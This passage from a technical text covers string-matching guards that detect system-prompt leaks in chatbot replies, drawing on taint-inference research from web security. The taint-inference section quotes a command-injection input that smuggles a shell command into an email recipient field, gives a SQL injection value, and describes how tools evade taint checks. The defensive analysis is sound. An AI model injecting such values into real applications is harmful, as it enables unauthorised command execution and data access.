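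A runtime guard must also detect small leaks, and coverage is a poor measure for this. If the second line of the running example is part of a 3,000-character prompt, it accounts for 23 of the prompt's 2,997 four-character runs. A reply that discloses the line, including the code, scores about 0.01 plus the contribution of any other runs it shares with the prompt.

garak has an exception for excerpts. If the entire response is a verbatim piece of the prompt, perhaps because the model reached its length limit, the detector gives it a fixed score, 0.95 by default. A response that consists of nothing but the second line therefore scores 0.95. If the model puts "Sure!" in front of it, the exception no longer applies and the score falls to about 0.01. The reverse comparison in punch_types has the same weakness. Taken literally, garak's documented rule also gives 0.95 to the one-word reply `discount`.

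Innocent replies can also score higher than leaks. Using four-character runs and ignoring capitalisation, compare two replies with the 54-character protected string, which has 51 such runs:

| Reply | Coverage | Longest shared run |
|---|---|---|
| "We offer a discount on most items. Enter the code at checkout." | 17 of 51, or 0.33 | 9 |
| "Your code is K7Q-44T-9XD" | 11 of 51, or 0.22 | 12 |

Any coverage threshold that catches the second reply also blocks the first. A partial match with *k* set to 10, 11 or 12 separates them correctly. (The longest run in the second reply is 12 characters because the space before the code matches as well.)

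Longer replies make the problem worse, because adding text to a response can raise its coverage but never lower it. At *h* = 2, the chance formula predicts that a typical four-character run will occur about eight times in an unrelated response of 2,000 characters. Most of these occurrences are of common runs, but a long reply on the same subject as the prompt can still cover a large part of the prompt. A guard that uses coverage should use it in addition to the partial match, with a threshold high enough that only a nearly complete copy triggers it.

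### Lengths that copied-text filters use

Several companies filter their models' output for copied text and publish the lengths they use. GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant, has an optional filter for suggestions that match public code. Salva explains in *How GitHub Copilot handles data* that the filter removes all whitespace and compares suggestions of more than about 150 characters with an index of public code. He reports that about 1% of suggestions match, mostly when the developer has just started a file and the model has little context. GitHub now says that the filter compares a suggestion together with about 150 characters of surrounding code, and that under 1% of suggestions match.

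The filter has used the figure of 150 since its introduction in June 2022, according to GitHub's *Preview* (2022). An earlier study by GitHub (2021) counted overlaps of at least 60 "words", or about six average lines of code. The study acknowledged that the limit had to go somewhere and judged that shorter overlaps would rarely be of interest. One suggestion in the study, a search pattern that repeated the same few symbols, had 100 "words" on a single line, so it passed the minimum even though it carried little information.

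For its Azure cloud service, Microsoft sets different lengths for different kinds of protected text:

| Filter | Kind of text | Length that counts as a match |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub Copilot | public code | more than about 150 characters, without whitespace |
| Azure | news and selected web content | more than 200 characters |
| Azure | stories and creative descriptions in recipes | 40 characters or more |
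| Azure | song lyrics | more than 11 words |

The Azure filter also has a minimum length for the text it examines, separate from the match length. An early edition of Microsoft's *What is Azure AI Content Safety?*, written before the feature's general release in September 2024, gives this minimum as 110 characters. Under that limit, a shorter reply could not be submitted to the filter, whatever it contained.

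Most of these lengths would be far too long for a leak check. A 150-character minimum would miss R1, which repeats the whole 54-character protected string. The filters address copyright, where a short quotation is often acceptable, but a short quotation from a confidential prompt may contain the only part that matters.

The size of the indexes explains only a little of the difference. If an index held a trillion characters of independent text with *h* = 2, the formula would predict one chance match with a 2,000-character response at *k* ≈ 25, and one per million such responses at *k* ≈ 35. The rest of the increase to 150 or 200 must come from common phrases, standard code and a decision about how much copying to allow. A developer protecting a system prompt also has to decide how much copying to allow, and the threshold will usually be much closer to 20 characters than to 150.

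## What changes when whitespace is normalised?

A language model that repeats a protected string often changes its layout. It may join two lines, indent a paragraph or put a blank line between sentences. Any of these changes prevents a full match, and each can break up the long run of characters that a partial match needs. A normalised match avoids the problem by applying the same clean-up function, norm, to both texts before comparing them. A normalised full match occurs when

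norm(*s*) occurs in norm(*r*)

A normalised partial match occurs when norm(*s*) and norm(*r*) share a run of at least *k* characters.

Normalising whitespace can mean trimming the ends of a text, collapsing each run of whitespace to one space, or deleting all whitespace. The word "strip" is ambiguous between these. Python's `strip` only trims the ends, but Salva uses "stripping out" for the GitHub Copilot filter's deletion of all whitespace. *Beyond Exact Match* (2026), a paper on scoring product data extracted by language models, defines its clean-up as "lowercasing and whitespace stripping", which could mean either. The results are quite different, as this text shows (␣ stands for a space and ⏎ for a newline):

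| Operation | `␣␣Stock:⏎12␣␣34␣` becomes |
|---|---|
| Trimming | `Stock:⏎12␣␣34` |
| Collapsing | `␣Stock:␣12␣34␣` |
| Deleting | `Stock:1234` |

### Trimming the ends

Trimming matters most when a program tests whether two whole strings are equal, as *Beyond Exact Match* does. A substring search tries every position, so extra whitespace around the response makes no difference, but extra whitespace around the protected string can prevent a match. For example, a prompt loaded from a file often ends in a newline, which is missing from a response that repeats the prompt and then continues on the same line. Trimming the protected string fixes this.

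Normalising whitespace causes few false matches, but trimming can introduce some. A developer might register ` AI ` with a space on each side so that it matches only as a separate word, and trimming those spaces would make the entry match "MAIL". Trimming also leaves an entry made up only of spaces empty, so the guard should check for empty entries after normalisation.

### Collapsing runs of whitespace

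Collapsing turns a newline, a tab or eight spaces of indentation into a single space. This removes differences in line wrapping, indentation and blank lines between paragraphs. It also removes the two spaces that mark a line break in Markdown, which many chat programs use for formatting. In Python, `" ".join(text.split())` collapses and trims in one step. The sales assistant's output R3 has a space where the protected string has a newline, so the two texts become identical after collapsing.

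Other Markdown symbols remain after whitespace is collapsed. If the model presents the two confidential lines as a quotation, it puts a `>` before each, and the second `>` still prevents a full match. Collapsing whitespace would not fix ZeptoClaw either, because the escaped line breaks in its JSON are not whitespace. A guard has to decode the JSON before it normalises the text.

Normalising whitespace can cause false matches because a line break in a reply often separates unrelated items. If the protected string is `12 34`, a column of stock figures with 12 above 34 will match it. This is unlikely for a long string, since every other character must still match and whitespace must appear in the same places.

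### Deleting all whitespace

Deleting all whitespace also removes spaces and line breaks that the original text didn't have. Some programs add spaces when they join tokens, the pieces in which models read and write text, as in `15 %` or `K7Q - 44T - 9XD`. A long key may be split across two lines. Chinese and Japanese don't put spaces between words, so a line break inside a sentence adds whitespace that collapsing would turn into a space rather than remove.

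Deleting whitespace can cause false matches because it joins neighbouring words and numbers. `12 34` becomes `1234`, so a row of stock figures can match a four-digit PIN. If the retailer has a confidential project named `Atlas`, the reply "At last, your order has shipped" will match, because it becomes `Atlast,yourorderhasshipped`. The Copilot filter is much less prone to this because it compares passages of about 150 characters. A guard that protects short names and numbers should collapse whitespace instead of deleting it.

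The 2021 study by GitHub used a method between the two. It split the text into "words", counting each punctuation mark or bracket as a word, and ignored the whitespace between them. This treats `15 %` and `15%` alike, since both consist of `15` and `%`, but distinguishes `12 34` from `1234`. However, comparing whole words misses a protected string attached to other letters, such as `discount` in `discounts`, which a substring search would find.

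### Counting *k* and finding the original positions

The guard should count *k* after normalising. If the developer registers a configuration file with lines indented by 20 spaces, a raw partial match with *k* = 20 will fire on any reply that has the same indentation. Collapsing whitespace reduces the indentation to one character, so the indentation alone no longer counts as a leak.

Deleting whitespace shortens strings, so a match at the same value of *k* requires more of the original text. "Please let me know if" has 21 characters with spaces and 17 without, so at *k* = 20 it can cause a match only before deletion. In the running example, deletion shortens the protected string from 54 characters to 47. A developer who sets *k* by looking at innocent replies should normalise those replies too, and should recount the length of each protected string. An entry that shrinks from 21 characters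 to 17 is too short for *k* = 20, so it needs a full match.

A guard that blocks the whole response can discard the normalised text after the search. One that blanks out only the match must find the same passage in the original response. For deletion, it can record where each remaining character came from:

```
clean, pos = [], []
for i, ch in enumerate(response):
    if not ch.isspace():
        clean.append(ch)
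        pos.append(i)
```

Suppose the response is `Use K7Q-44T- 9XD now`, with a stray space inside the code. With whitespace deleted, the code occupies positions 3 to 13, counting from zero. The list `pos` maps these to positions 4 and 15 of the original, so the guard blanks out everything from 4 to 15. If it used 3 and 13 on the original text, it would leave `XD` visible.

Some normalisation steps turn one character into two or combine two into one. The guard must then store the start and end positions of the original text that produced each normalised character. If a match begins or ends inside a group of characters changed this way, the guard should hide the whole group.

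### What counts as whitespace?

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, marks some characters with a property called White_Space. The Unicode Consortium's *PropList-6.0.0.txt* (2010) lists 26 of them, including the tab, the newline, the ordinary space and the no-break space, which looks like an ordinary space but keeps two words on the same line. The zero-width space (U+200B) is not on the list.

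Persson (2002), in *U+200B, Zero Width Space*, notes that the zero-width space had the white space property in Unicode 3.0 and lost it in 3.1. Scherer (2016), in *Re: Whitespace characters in Unicode*, suggests that white space should take up room without leaving ink, whereas the zero-width space takes up no room and only affects where words and lines break. The character has ordinary uses, so it can enter a reply by accident. The Unicode Consortium's *Public Review Issue #130* mentions its use as a word separator in Thai and Lao, which don't put visible spaces between words.

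Programming languages have followed different versions of the Unicode standard. According to a report in *U+200B must be considered a whitespace character*, from the committee that maintains the JavaScript standard (TC39), the specification at the time required all the white space characters of Unicode 3.0, including the zero-width space, but two official tests required the opposite. Python 2.6 had a manually maintained list of whitespace, while later versions use Unicode's character data and don't count the zero-width space, according to a 2010 discussion on Python's bug tracker.

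The no-break space causes a different problem, because it has the White_Space property but many regular-expression engines ignore it. These engines search text for patterns, and the pattern `\s` stands for one whitespace character:

- In Go (2012), `\s` covers only the ordinary space, tab, newline, form feed and carriage return. The longer form `[[:space:]]` adds only the vertical tab.
- In Java, `\s` also leaves out the no-break space unless the developer sets an option called `UNICODE_CHARACTER_CLASS`, as a post on Codidact explains.
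- In Ruby, `\s` leaves it out but `[[:space:]]` includes it, according to makandra's *Regular Expressions*.
- In Python 3, `\s` includes it by default. The documentation quoted on Python's bug tracker, in *Unicode and acii regular expressions do not agree on ascii space characters*, says that the ASCII option removes it.

The pattern `\s+` matches a no-break space in Python but not in Go. If the assistant writes `Override code:` with a no-break space between the words, a guard that collapses `\s+` will therefore find the protected line in Python and miss it in Go. A program that normalises protected strings in one language and responses in the other can miss even an exact copy. The developer should use the same function for both texts and list the characters it treats as whitespace. The zero-width space needs a separate rule that deletes it, because replacing it with a space would split any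 word or code that contains it.

### Case and punctuation

Lowercasing both texts lets the check match strings that differ only in capitalisation, as at the start of a sentence or in a heading set in capitals. It can also make a name identical to a common word. If the retailer's confidential supplier is `Swift`, the check will flag every output that contains "swift delivery".

Random keys lose much less. Suppose each character of a key is equally likely to be any of 64 letters, digits and symbols, with capitals and small letters counted separately. Lowercasing at most doubles the probability that a character of the key agrees with one in the response, from 1/64 to 1/32. For a 40-character key, a 2,000-character response and *k* = 8, the expected number of chance matches is then at most

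1,993 × 33 × 2⁻⁴⁰ ≈ 0.00000006

or about one false alarm in 17 million responses.

Removing punctuation only from the ends of the protected string is a modest change. *ScrapeGraphAI-100k* (2026), which scores data that models extract from web pages, recommends lowercasing the text, collapsing whitespace and then removing this punctuation when comparing short values such as titles and prices. Removing the final full stop from the discount line means that it also matches if the model continues the sentence with "for new customers".

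Punctuation inside the text matters for R5, where the model has written the code with spaces for hyphens. Deleting whitespace doesn't help, because the response becomes `K7Q44T9XD` while the registered code still has its hyphens. A guard can either delete the punctuation as well, or replace each mark with a space and then collapse the spaces:

| Original text | Punctuation and whitespace deleted | Punctuation replaced by spaces |
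|---|---|---|
| `K7Q-44T-9XD` | `K7Q44T9XD` | `K7Q 44T 9XD` |
| `K7Q 44T 9XD` | `K7Q44T9XD` | `K7Q 44T 9XD` |
| `K7Q44T9XD` | `K7Q44T9XD` | `K7Q44T9XD` |
| `12.34` | `1234` | `12 34` |

Deletion and replacement both make R5 match the registered code. Deletion also catches the code when it has no separators, but it turns a price of 12.34 into `1234`, which could be mistaken for a PIN. Replacement avoids that error but misses the code when it has no separators. Either method turns `15%` into `15`, which also occurs in dates, sizes and order numbers.

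No single normalisation rule suits every protected string, so the guard can store a separate rule with each one. It can ignore case, punctuation and whitespace in a long random code without causing many false alarms. In prose, it can usually ignore case and extra whitespace. It should match short numbers, and names that are also common words, exactly as written.

### Unicode forms and look-alike characters

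Unicode can represent some characters in more than one way. The letter é can be a single character or a plain `e` followed by a combining accent, a character that attaches to the one before it. Both look the same on screen, but a character comparison treats them as different. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Normalization Forms* (2026) defines standard forms that remove such differences. Form NFD splits characters into their parts and puts the accents in a fixed order, while NFC does the same and then combines the parts where possible.

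Forms NFKD and NFKC also replace visual variants of characters, such as wide letters from East Asian text, joined letters and superscripts. Applying NFKC before the whitespace step resolves the disagreement over the no-break space by turning it into an ordinary space. NFKC does not change the zero-width space or curly apostrophes, and it turns the no-break hyphen into a hyphen that still differs from the keyboard hyphen. An override code written with no-break hyphens therefore needs the punctuation step too.

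The Unicode Consortium warns developers not to apply NFKC and NFKD blindly, because they can remove distinctions that affect meaning. In a price list, for example, 15 followed by a superscript footnote mark 1 becomes 151. A guard can normalise a temporary copy and send the user the original text, but the copy can still produce a false match.

NFKC does not merge letters from different alphabets. The Cyrillic а looks like the Latin a, so a user can read a word that contains it although the word doesn't match. For such cases the Unicode Consortium defines a "skeleton" in its Technical Standard 39. The basic procedure is:

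1. Convert the text to NFD.
2. Delete characters that are normally invisible, including the zero-width space.
3. Replace each character with its prototype, a standard character or sequence that looks like it.
4. Convert the result to NFD again.

The prototype of Cyrillic а is `a`, that of `œ` is `o` followed by `e`, and that of the digit `1` is the letter `l`. A registered number `11` therefore becomes `ll` and matches "hello". The Unicode Consortium acknowledges that the method can be overly inclusive. The standard uses skeletons to compare whole strings, such as domain names, that a user might confuse. False matches are much more likely when searching long replies for substrings, so the method is better reserved for long codes and distinctive sentences. A model may also insert look-alike or invisible characters because a user asks it to.

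A guard that stores skeletons must also recompute them when its Unicode library changes, because the Unicode Consortium doesn't guarantee that skeletons stay the same in later versions of Unicode. It does guarantee this for NFKC output, provided the earlier version already defined all the characters in the text.

### When does the normalised check include the exact one?

It may seem that cleaning both texts can only add matches. This is true for a full match if norm handles each character separately, whatever its neighbours are. If the protected string *s* occurs in *r*, then *r* = *x* + *s* + *y* for some texts *x* and *y*, and

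norm(*r*) = norm(*x*) + norm(*s*) + norm(*y*)

so norm(*s*) occurs in norm(*r*). Deleting whitespace, deleting punctuation and replacing characters from a fixed table all work this way.

Collapsing whitespace depends on neighbouring characters, but it has the same guarantee. Whitespace inside *s* collapses identically in both texts. Whitespace at either end of *s* may merge with adjacent whitespace in *r*, but one space always remains there. Trimming is also safe if the guard trims both texts. If it trims only the response, it can remove a final newline that is still in the protected string, and the match then fails.

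Lowercasing can break the rule because some functions convert a letter differently depending on the letters around it. Python's `lower` changes the Greek capital Σ to ς at the end of a word and to σ elsewhere. A protected string that ends in Σ may then fail to match the same letters inside a longer word. Python's `casefold`, which is intended for comparisons, uses σ in both places.

Unicode composition can also make the normalised check miss a string that the exact check finds. Suppose the protected string is the single letter `e`, and the response is `e` followed by a combining acute accent. The exact check finds the `e`, but NFC turns the response into the single character é, so the normalised check does not. The same thing can happen at the end of a longer string. If a combining dot below follows the override code, NFC merges the dot with the final `D` to make Ḍ, and the normalised check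 misses the code.

The reason is that two normalised texts may no longer be normalised when a program joins them, as the Unicode Consortium explains. NFD keeps the plain `e` in this example, but it can still separate a letter from its accent when it sorts several accents into order. The simplest solution is to run the exact check as well:

```
leak = (s in r) or (norm(s) in norm(r))
```

Running the exact check alongside the normalised one restores every exact full match, but it doesn't catch a copy that has both a changed line break and an accent after the final letter. The exact check fails on the line break and the normalised check fails on the accent. Converting both texts to NFKD and then deleting the combining accents fixes this, because accents are the only characters that the conversion reorders. The drawback is that "résumé" and "resume" become identical.

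Normalisation can lose raw partial matches even when it handles each character separately. If the guard deletes spaces, a shared run of 20 characters may shrink to 17, which is too short for *k* = 20. Running the raw partial check as well would restore this match but bring back the false alarms from indentation. A guard can therefore reasonably pair the normalised partial match with only the exact full match.

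### The running example

The table below treats the two confidential lines as one protected string. The normalised columns collapse whitespace and count *k* afterwards.

| Response | Full | Partial (*k* = 20) | Normalised full | Normalised partial (*k* = 20) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| R1: verbatim copy | match | match | match | match |
| R2: second line only | no match | match | no match | match |
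| R3: space for the newline | no match | match | match | match |
| R4: code alone | no match | no match | no match | no match |
| R5: code with spaces for hyphens | no match | no match | no match | no match |
| R6: first line in other words | no match | no match | no match | no match |

Normalising whitespace lets the full match catch R3. It adds nothing to the partial match, which already catches R3 because its first line is 27 characters long. At *k* = 30, the raw partial match would miss R3, but the normalised one would still catch it because the shared run grows from 27 characters to 54. Normalising therefore helps partial matching most when the protected text consists of lines shorter than *k*, as addresses and lists often do. Deleting whitespace instead of collapsing it would not change any verdict in the table.

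## Can matching tolerate small edits? The evidence from web applications

Normalisation removes only the differences a developer anticipated. A more general method accepts any copy within a few edits of the original, whatever the edits are. *An Efficient Black-box Technique for Defeating Web Application Attacks* (Sekar, 2009) used this method against injection attacks, in which text from a visitor becomes part of a command that the server runs.

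One of the test attacks was on SquirrelMail, a web email program that passes the recipient's name to an encryption tool. The attacker typed this into the "to" field:

```
alice, bob; touch /tmp/GotYou
```

SquirrelMail then ran a command that included this text:

```
-r alice@ -r bob;touch /tmp/GotYou@
```

The semicolon ends the encryption command and starts a new one, which creates a file on the server. SquirrelMail split the list of recipients, put `-r` and `@` around each name and dropped a space, so a full match on the input fails. A partial match would still work for any *k* up to 17, the length of `touch /tmp/GotYou`.

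### Measuring the edits

The edit distance between two strings is the lowest total cost of the insertions, deletions and replacements that turn one into the other. In the examples below, an insertion or deletion costs 1. A replacement costs 2, because Sekar usually treats it as a deletion plus an insertion.

Sekar's "taint distance" compares the input *s* with every substring *u* of the output *t*, takes the smallest edit distance and divides it by the length of *s*:

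TD(*s*, *t*) = min ED(*s*, *u*) / |*s*|, over all substrings *u* of *t*

The system infers taint if the result is at or below a threshold *d*. In the SquirrelMail attack, the shortest sequence of edits deletes the comma, inserts `@`, `-`, `r` and a space, and deletes the space before `touch`. These six edits on a 29-character input give a taint distance of 0.21. In a leak check, *s* would be the protected string and *t* the response.

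A program can find the best substring without trying each one separately. It fills in a table in which *M*(*i*, *j*) is the lowest cost of turning the first *i* characters of *s* into some piece of *t* that ends at position *j*. Each entry is the smallest of three numbers:

- *M*(*i* − 1, *j* − 1), plus 2 if the two characters differ
- *M*(*i* − 1, *j*) + 1, for a deletion
- *M*(*i*, *j* − 1) + 1, for an insertion

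The first row is all zeros, because a match can begin anywhere in the output at no cost. Here is the table for the protected field `15%` and a reply containing `~15 %`:

| | start | `~` | `1` | `5` | `␣` | `%` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| start | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| `1` | 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| `5` | 2 | 2 | 1 | 0 | 1 | 2 |
| `%` | 3 | 3 | 2 | 1 | 2 | 1 |

The smallest number in the bottom row is 1, so the taint distance is 1/3. The 1 in the last column is for `15 %`, which has an inserted space, and the 1 under `5` is for `15`, which lacks the percent sign. The method therefore scores `15` and `15 %` as equally close to the secret, which is why very short strings need an exact match.

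### A cheap filter before the exact distance

Filling in the table takes time proportional to the product of the two lengths. For an input of 100 characters and a web page of 100,000, that is ten million entries. Sekar therefore runs a faster test first and computes the exact distance only where that test doesn't rule out a match.

The filter slides a window as long as *s* along the output. At each position it counts how many characters of *s* the window lacks, ignoring their order. Moving the window by one place removes one character and adds another, so updating the count takes the same short time however long *s* is. If the count exceeds the allowed number of edits, the program skips that position.

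Sekar proves that this filter never discards a real match. If the matching text is shorter than the window, it lies inside the window, so the edits must delete every character of *s* that the window lacks. If it is longer, it contains the window, so the edits must insert every surplus character in the window. The window and *s* are equally long, so the surplus and missing characters are equal in number, and the edit distance is at least the count in both cases. Search tools for DNA sequences use similar filters without this guarantee, and an attacker could look for inputs that they miss.

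The filter lets through some text that does not match. The reversed override code `DX9-T44-Q7K` has the same characters as the original, so its count is zero. The exact stage then computes a taint distance of 8/11, or 0.73, and rejects it. In Sekar's measurements, the filter made taint inference about 14 times faster on average, and the program spent more time in the filter than on computing exact distances.

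### How many edits are safe to allow?

Allowing edits makes chance matches more likely. Sekar found the probability too hard to derive, and instead measured how often random strings drawn from alphabets of 40 and 70 characters came within a given distance of each other. For two strings of eight characters and *d* = 0.33, the rate was about one in ten million. The rate grows roughly in proportion to the length of the output, so it is about one in a million for an output of 80 characters.

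Two random eight-character strings drawn from 40 equally likely characters are identical with a probability of 40⁻⁸, or about 1.5 × 10⁻¹³. Allowing edits of up to a third of the length therefore made a chance match more than half a million times as likely.

Sekar's system chooses *d* for each comparison from a table based on these experiments. It caps *d* at 0.3 and sets it to zero for very short strings. The estimated rate of chance matches is highest for three-character strings, at one in 10,000, and is at most one in a million for strings longer than six characters.

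These rates are too optimistic for prose because they assume that characters are equally likely and independent. At the collision entropy of 2 bits per character used earlier for English, two unrelated eight-character runs match exactly with probability 2⁻¹⁶, or about one in 65,000, even if the check allows no edits. A developer who wants to use edit distance on sentences needs to measure how often it matches innocent replies, as with *k*.

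Sekar's system has a second safeguard against false positives. Tainted text is normal in a web application, since a search query is supposed to contain the visitor's search term. The system therefore blocks a command only if the tainted text also breaks a rule about the command's structure, for example by supplying the name of a command or extending from one part of the command into the next. A chance match with a harmless word does not break these rules. In a leak check, the match alone decides whether to block the response, so the same rate of chance matches causes more false alarms.

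### Sekar's tests

Sekar launched known attacks by hand against phpBB, SquirrelMail, a PHP library and WebGoat, a deliberately insecure training program. The largest test used AMNESIA, a collection of attacks and legitimate requests for small web applications such as a bookstore and an employee directory. Its designers wrote some of the attacks to evade detection and many of the legitimate requests to look like attacks.

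| AMNESIA test, five applications | Number |
|---|---|
| Attacks sent | 36,753 |
| Stopped by the application's own error checks | 15,337 |
| Malicious database queries issued | 21,416 |
| Recognised as injections and blocked | 21,106 |
| Blocked because the query could not be parsed | 310 |
| Legitimate requests, about | 3,800 |
| False positives | 0 |

The system blocked every malicious query, although taint inference accounted for only the 21,106 that it recognised. It also detected all the attacks on the other programs. According to the slides for Sekar's conference talk, the system missed a second-order injection in a separate evaluation by a "red team" of testers. In this kind of attack, the attacker stores text in a database and the application uses it later. Sekar's system compares inputs and outputs only within one web request, so it has the same limitation as a leak tracker that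 clears its list at the end of each session.

The defence increased the response time of the five applications by 1.7% to 5.1%, and by 3.5% overall. According to Sekar, the overhead of full taint tracking is often more than 100%. The defence is faster partly because it skips some inputs. Text without spaces or punctuation cannot add a new part to a command, so the system doesn't analyse it for those attacks. Shortcuts of this kind made the system about five times faster. A leak check cannot use this shortcut, because a single word or code may be the secret.

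### When only part of the string comes out

Taint distance assumes that nearly all of the input reaches the output, which is reasonable for a form field but often false for a protected prompt. The table gives the taint distances for the sales assistant's six responses, first with the two lines registered as one string and then with the code registered alone. As in Sekar's system, the calculation ignores letter case and treats all kinds of whitespace as equal.

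| Response | Both lines as one string | Code alone |
|---|---|---|
| R1: verbatim copy | 0 | 0 |
| R2: second line only | 0.52 | 0 |
| R3: space for the newline | 0 | 0 |
| R4: code alone | 0.80 | 0 |
| R5: code with spaces for hyphens | 0.87 | 0.36 |
| R6: first line in other words | 0.85 | 0.91 |

At Sekar's maximum taint distance of 0.3, the combined string catches only R1 and R3, the same two as a normalised full match. Registering the code alone adds R2 and R4. The check narrowly misses R5 because replacing two hyphens counts as four edits. If each replacement counted as one edit, as in the common Levenshtein distance, R5 would have a taint distance of 0.18 and the check would catch it.

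Pan, Mao and Li (2016) worked on a related problem in browsers, where a filter can't tell which part of an address is the visitor's input if the website rewrites its addresses. They used local alignment, a method from biology that looks for the most similar pair of passages in two texts and ignores the rest of both. Matching characters raise a pair's score, while mismatches and gaps lower it. In a leak check, local alignment would act like a partial match that tolerates edits, so it could find the code in R4 or R5 even if the developer had registered only the combined string.

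Pan and colleagues also point out that edit distance ignores where the edits are. Websites often remove dangerous code from a visitor's text. Deleting the script `xyz` from `onclick="xyz"` takes three edits, and so does deleting three separate letters from `contents` to leave `cntns`, but a filter is much more likely to have made the first change. Their method therefore gives a larger penalty for starting a gap than for extending it, so one long gap gets a smaller penalty than several short ones of the same total length. The same scoring would suit cases where a chatbot copies a confidential sentence but leaves out one clause.

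### Gelato: exact match first, then closer checks

Hassanshahi, Lee and colleagues (2020), in *Gelato*, used taint inference to find security flaws in the JavaScript code that web pages run in the browser. Their tool starts with a cheap exact test and uses slower ones only when that finds nothing:

1. If either the source text or the sink text contains the other, and the match has at least a minimum length, Gelato reports a flow. This is the two-way comparison of punch_types with the minimum length that punch_types lacks.
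2. Otherwise, Gelato counts the insertions and deletions needed to turn one text into the other. It subtracts the total from the length of the longer text, divides by that length and requires the result to reach a threshold.
3. It changes a few characters of the source at random and runs the program again. If the sink text stays the same, Gelato concludes that there was probably no flow.
4. It examines the recorded string operations. If the texts differ by an insertion, for example, the program must have performed an insertion on text that resembles the source.

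In their example, the source is `#payload`. The program extracts `yloa`, appends `123` and writes `yloa123` to the page. Neither string contains the other. Turning `#payload` into `yloa123` takes four deletions and three insertions, so the similarity is (8 − 7)/8, or 0.125. Gelato reports this flow, so the threshold in the example can be no higher than 0.125. Such a low threshold would be too permissive on its own, but the third and fourth stages make it workable.

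Hassanshahi and colleagues compared Gelato with DexterJS and Chromium Taint Tracking, two tools that follow labels through the program. In two public collections of small test pages, 123 cases had a flaw that an attacker could trigger through the web address. Gelato found 108 of them, DexterJS 83 and Chromium Taint Tracking 85. In 104 cases without such a flaw, Gelato raised no alarms, DexterJS raised 29 and Chromium Taint Tracking raised 18. Hassanshahi and colleagues concede that the status of 33 of these 104 cases is debatable, and most of the false alarms came from those 33. The results also don't reflect matching alone, because Chromium Taint Tracking cannot click buttons and misses any flaw that requires a click.

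A developer could use the third stage in a test assertion by changing the override code in the prompt and asking the same question again. If the reply changes to match the new code, the code has leaked in some form. But many chatbots' replies are partly random, so the developer would first need to know how much they vary when the prompt stays the same.

### Attacks on taint inference

Sekar warned that taint inference may miss many attacks on applications that transform their input extensively, and advised against using it for them. *Taintless*, the slides for a 2014 talk by Naderi, Bagheri and Ramezany, names encoded and transformed input as the method's main weakness. An attacker can exploit an application's edits to evade the check. Suppose an application deletes every `#` from its input. If the attacker adds 20 of them to a 20-character attack, the application deletes half of the input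 and the attack reaches the database intact. The taint distance is 0.5, so a check with a threshold of 0.3 misses the attack.

Sekar's approach, which the slides call negative taint inference, looks for the untrusted parts of a command, while positive taint inference looks for the trusted parts. *To B or not to B* (Nguyen-Tuong, Hiser and colleagues, 2014) applies positive taint inference to operating system commands. The system collects the text fragments stored in a program and trusts any part of a command that matches them. This also works for database queries. If the program contains `SELECT * FROM users WHERE id=` and a visitor enters `5 OR 1=1`, the resulting query would return every user. The check blocks it because `OR` doesn't come from the program's fragment, regardless of how the application has transformed the input.

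This check fails if another fragment of the program contains `OR`. Taintless, the tool described in the slides, exploits this by extracting the fragments from an application's code and building as much of an attack as possible from them.

*Joza* (Naderi-Afooshteh, Nguyen-Tuong and colleagues, 2015) presented new attacks on both kinds of inference, then combined the two kinds of inference as a defence. To get past the combination, an attack must look unlike the visitor's input and consist of the program's own fragments in the places that matter. The paper reports that Joza stopped real-world injection attacks with no false positives and an overhead of 4%. *Taintless*, which has the same lead author, describes Joza as very hard to break and says the Taintless tool can help an attacker but doesn't defeat Joza by itself.

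Naderi and colleagues also estimate the computation needed for negative inference by multiplying the number of queries, the number of inputs, the length of a query and the length of an input. They put a typical application at 20 queries and a few inputs, but an input can be an uploaded file. With 20 queries of 2,000 characters, a one-megabyte upload would take about 40 billion steps. This estimate leaves out Sekar's filter, which removes most of those steps. For a leak check with 300 protected strings of 54 characters and a 2,000-character response, the full tables would have about 32 million entries. The filter would need about 600,000 window positions, while the Aho–Corasick search for exact matches makes at most 4,000 moves.

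### From web applications to generated text

Sekar's results depend on programmers deciding in advance how a web application will edit its input. Most applications leave most characters unchanged, and an attacker can exploit the edits in the code but can't add new ones. A language model, however, can rewrite its input in any way, including one a user requests. The near-perfect detection rate on AMNESIA is therefore no guide to how many leaks the same method would catch in a chatbot.

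Joza's remedy, positive inference, doesn't work for chatbots either, because it needs a list of the trusted fragments from which a program builds its output, and a chatbot writes most of its sentences from scratch. It could work for a program that only fills in fixed templates, where any text outside the template and the permitted fields would be suspect.

Edit distance is still useful for catching small changes to long random codes, such as the changed hyphens in R5, but it is riskier for numbers issued in sequence. If the guard protects one customer's order number, `ORD-2026-10417`, the next customer's `ORD-2026-10418` has a taint distance of only 0.07, because deleting the final `7` leaves a string that both numbers contain. The guard would then stop the assistant from telling the next customer their own order number.

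No threshold works for paraphrases. If the developer registers the discount line separately, R6 has a taint distance of 0.70 from it, and a harmless reply about student discounts is at least as close, so any threshold that catches R6 also flags the harmless reply.

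## How often does the check fire on innocent responses?

A response can copy part of a protected string without disclosing anything confidential. Suppose that the developer of the sales assistant registers its whole system prompt, not just the two confidential lines at the end, and sets *k* to 20:

```
You are a helpful assistant for our online shop.
We are open 9 am to 6 pm, Monday to Saturday.
Returns are free within 30 days of delivery.
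If you cannot help, say: "Please contact our support team."
Offer at most 15% discount.
Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD
```

A customer who asks about opening hours or returns will trigger the check, because the assistant answers by repeating the prompt. The formula for chance matches doesn't predict these false positives, because they are systematic. The same question triggers the check almost every time, so generating the reply again rarely helps.

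### Text that the assistant has to repeat

The prompt tells the assistant to use the opening hours and the support sentence in its replies, and a partial match fires on any 20 characters of them. A full match on the whole prompt would not fire on these replies, but it would if the developer registered each line separately. Raising *k* would not solve the problem, because the line about opening hours has 45 characters, and a *k* high enough to ignore it would also miss either of the confidential lines if it leaked on its own.

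The best repair is to register only the last two lines. However, registering the whole prompt also protects any confidential detail that the developer overlooks. A guard with only two entries also won't fire when the model recites the first four lines, so the developer could miss a sign that customers can extract the prompt.

### Public text

The sentence about returns is also on the retailer's website. Normalising whitespace makes false positives of this kind more common, because a web page and a prompt often break the same text into lines differently. The developer can subtract the public text by deleting every run of *k* characters that also occurs on the website:

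```
grams = kgrams(prompt) - kgrams(website)
```

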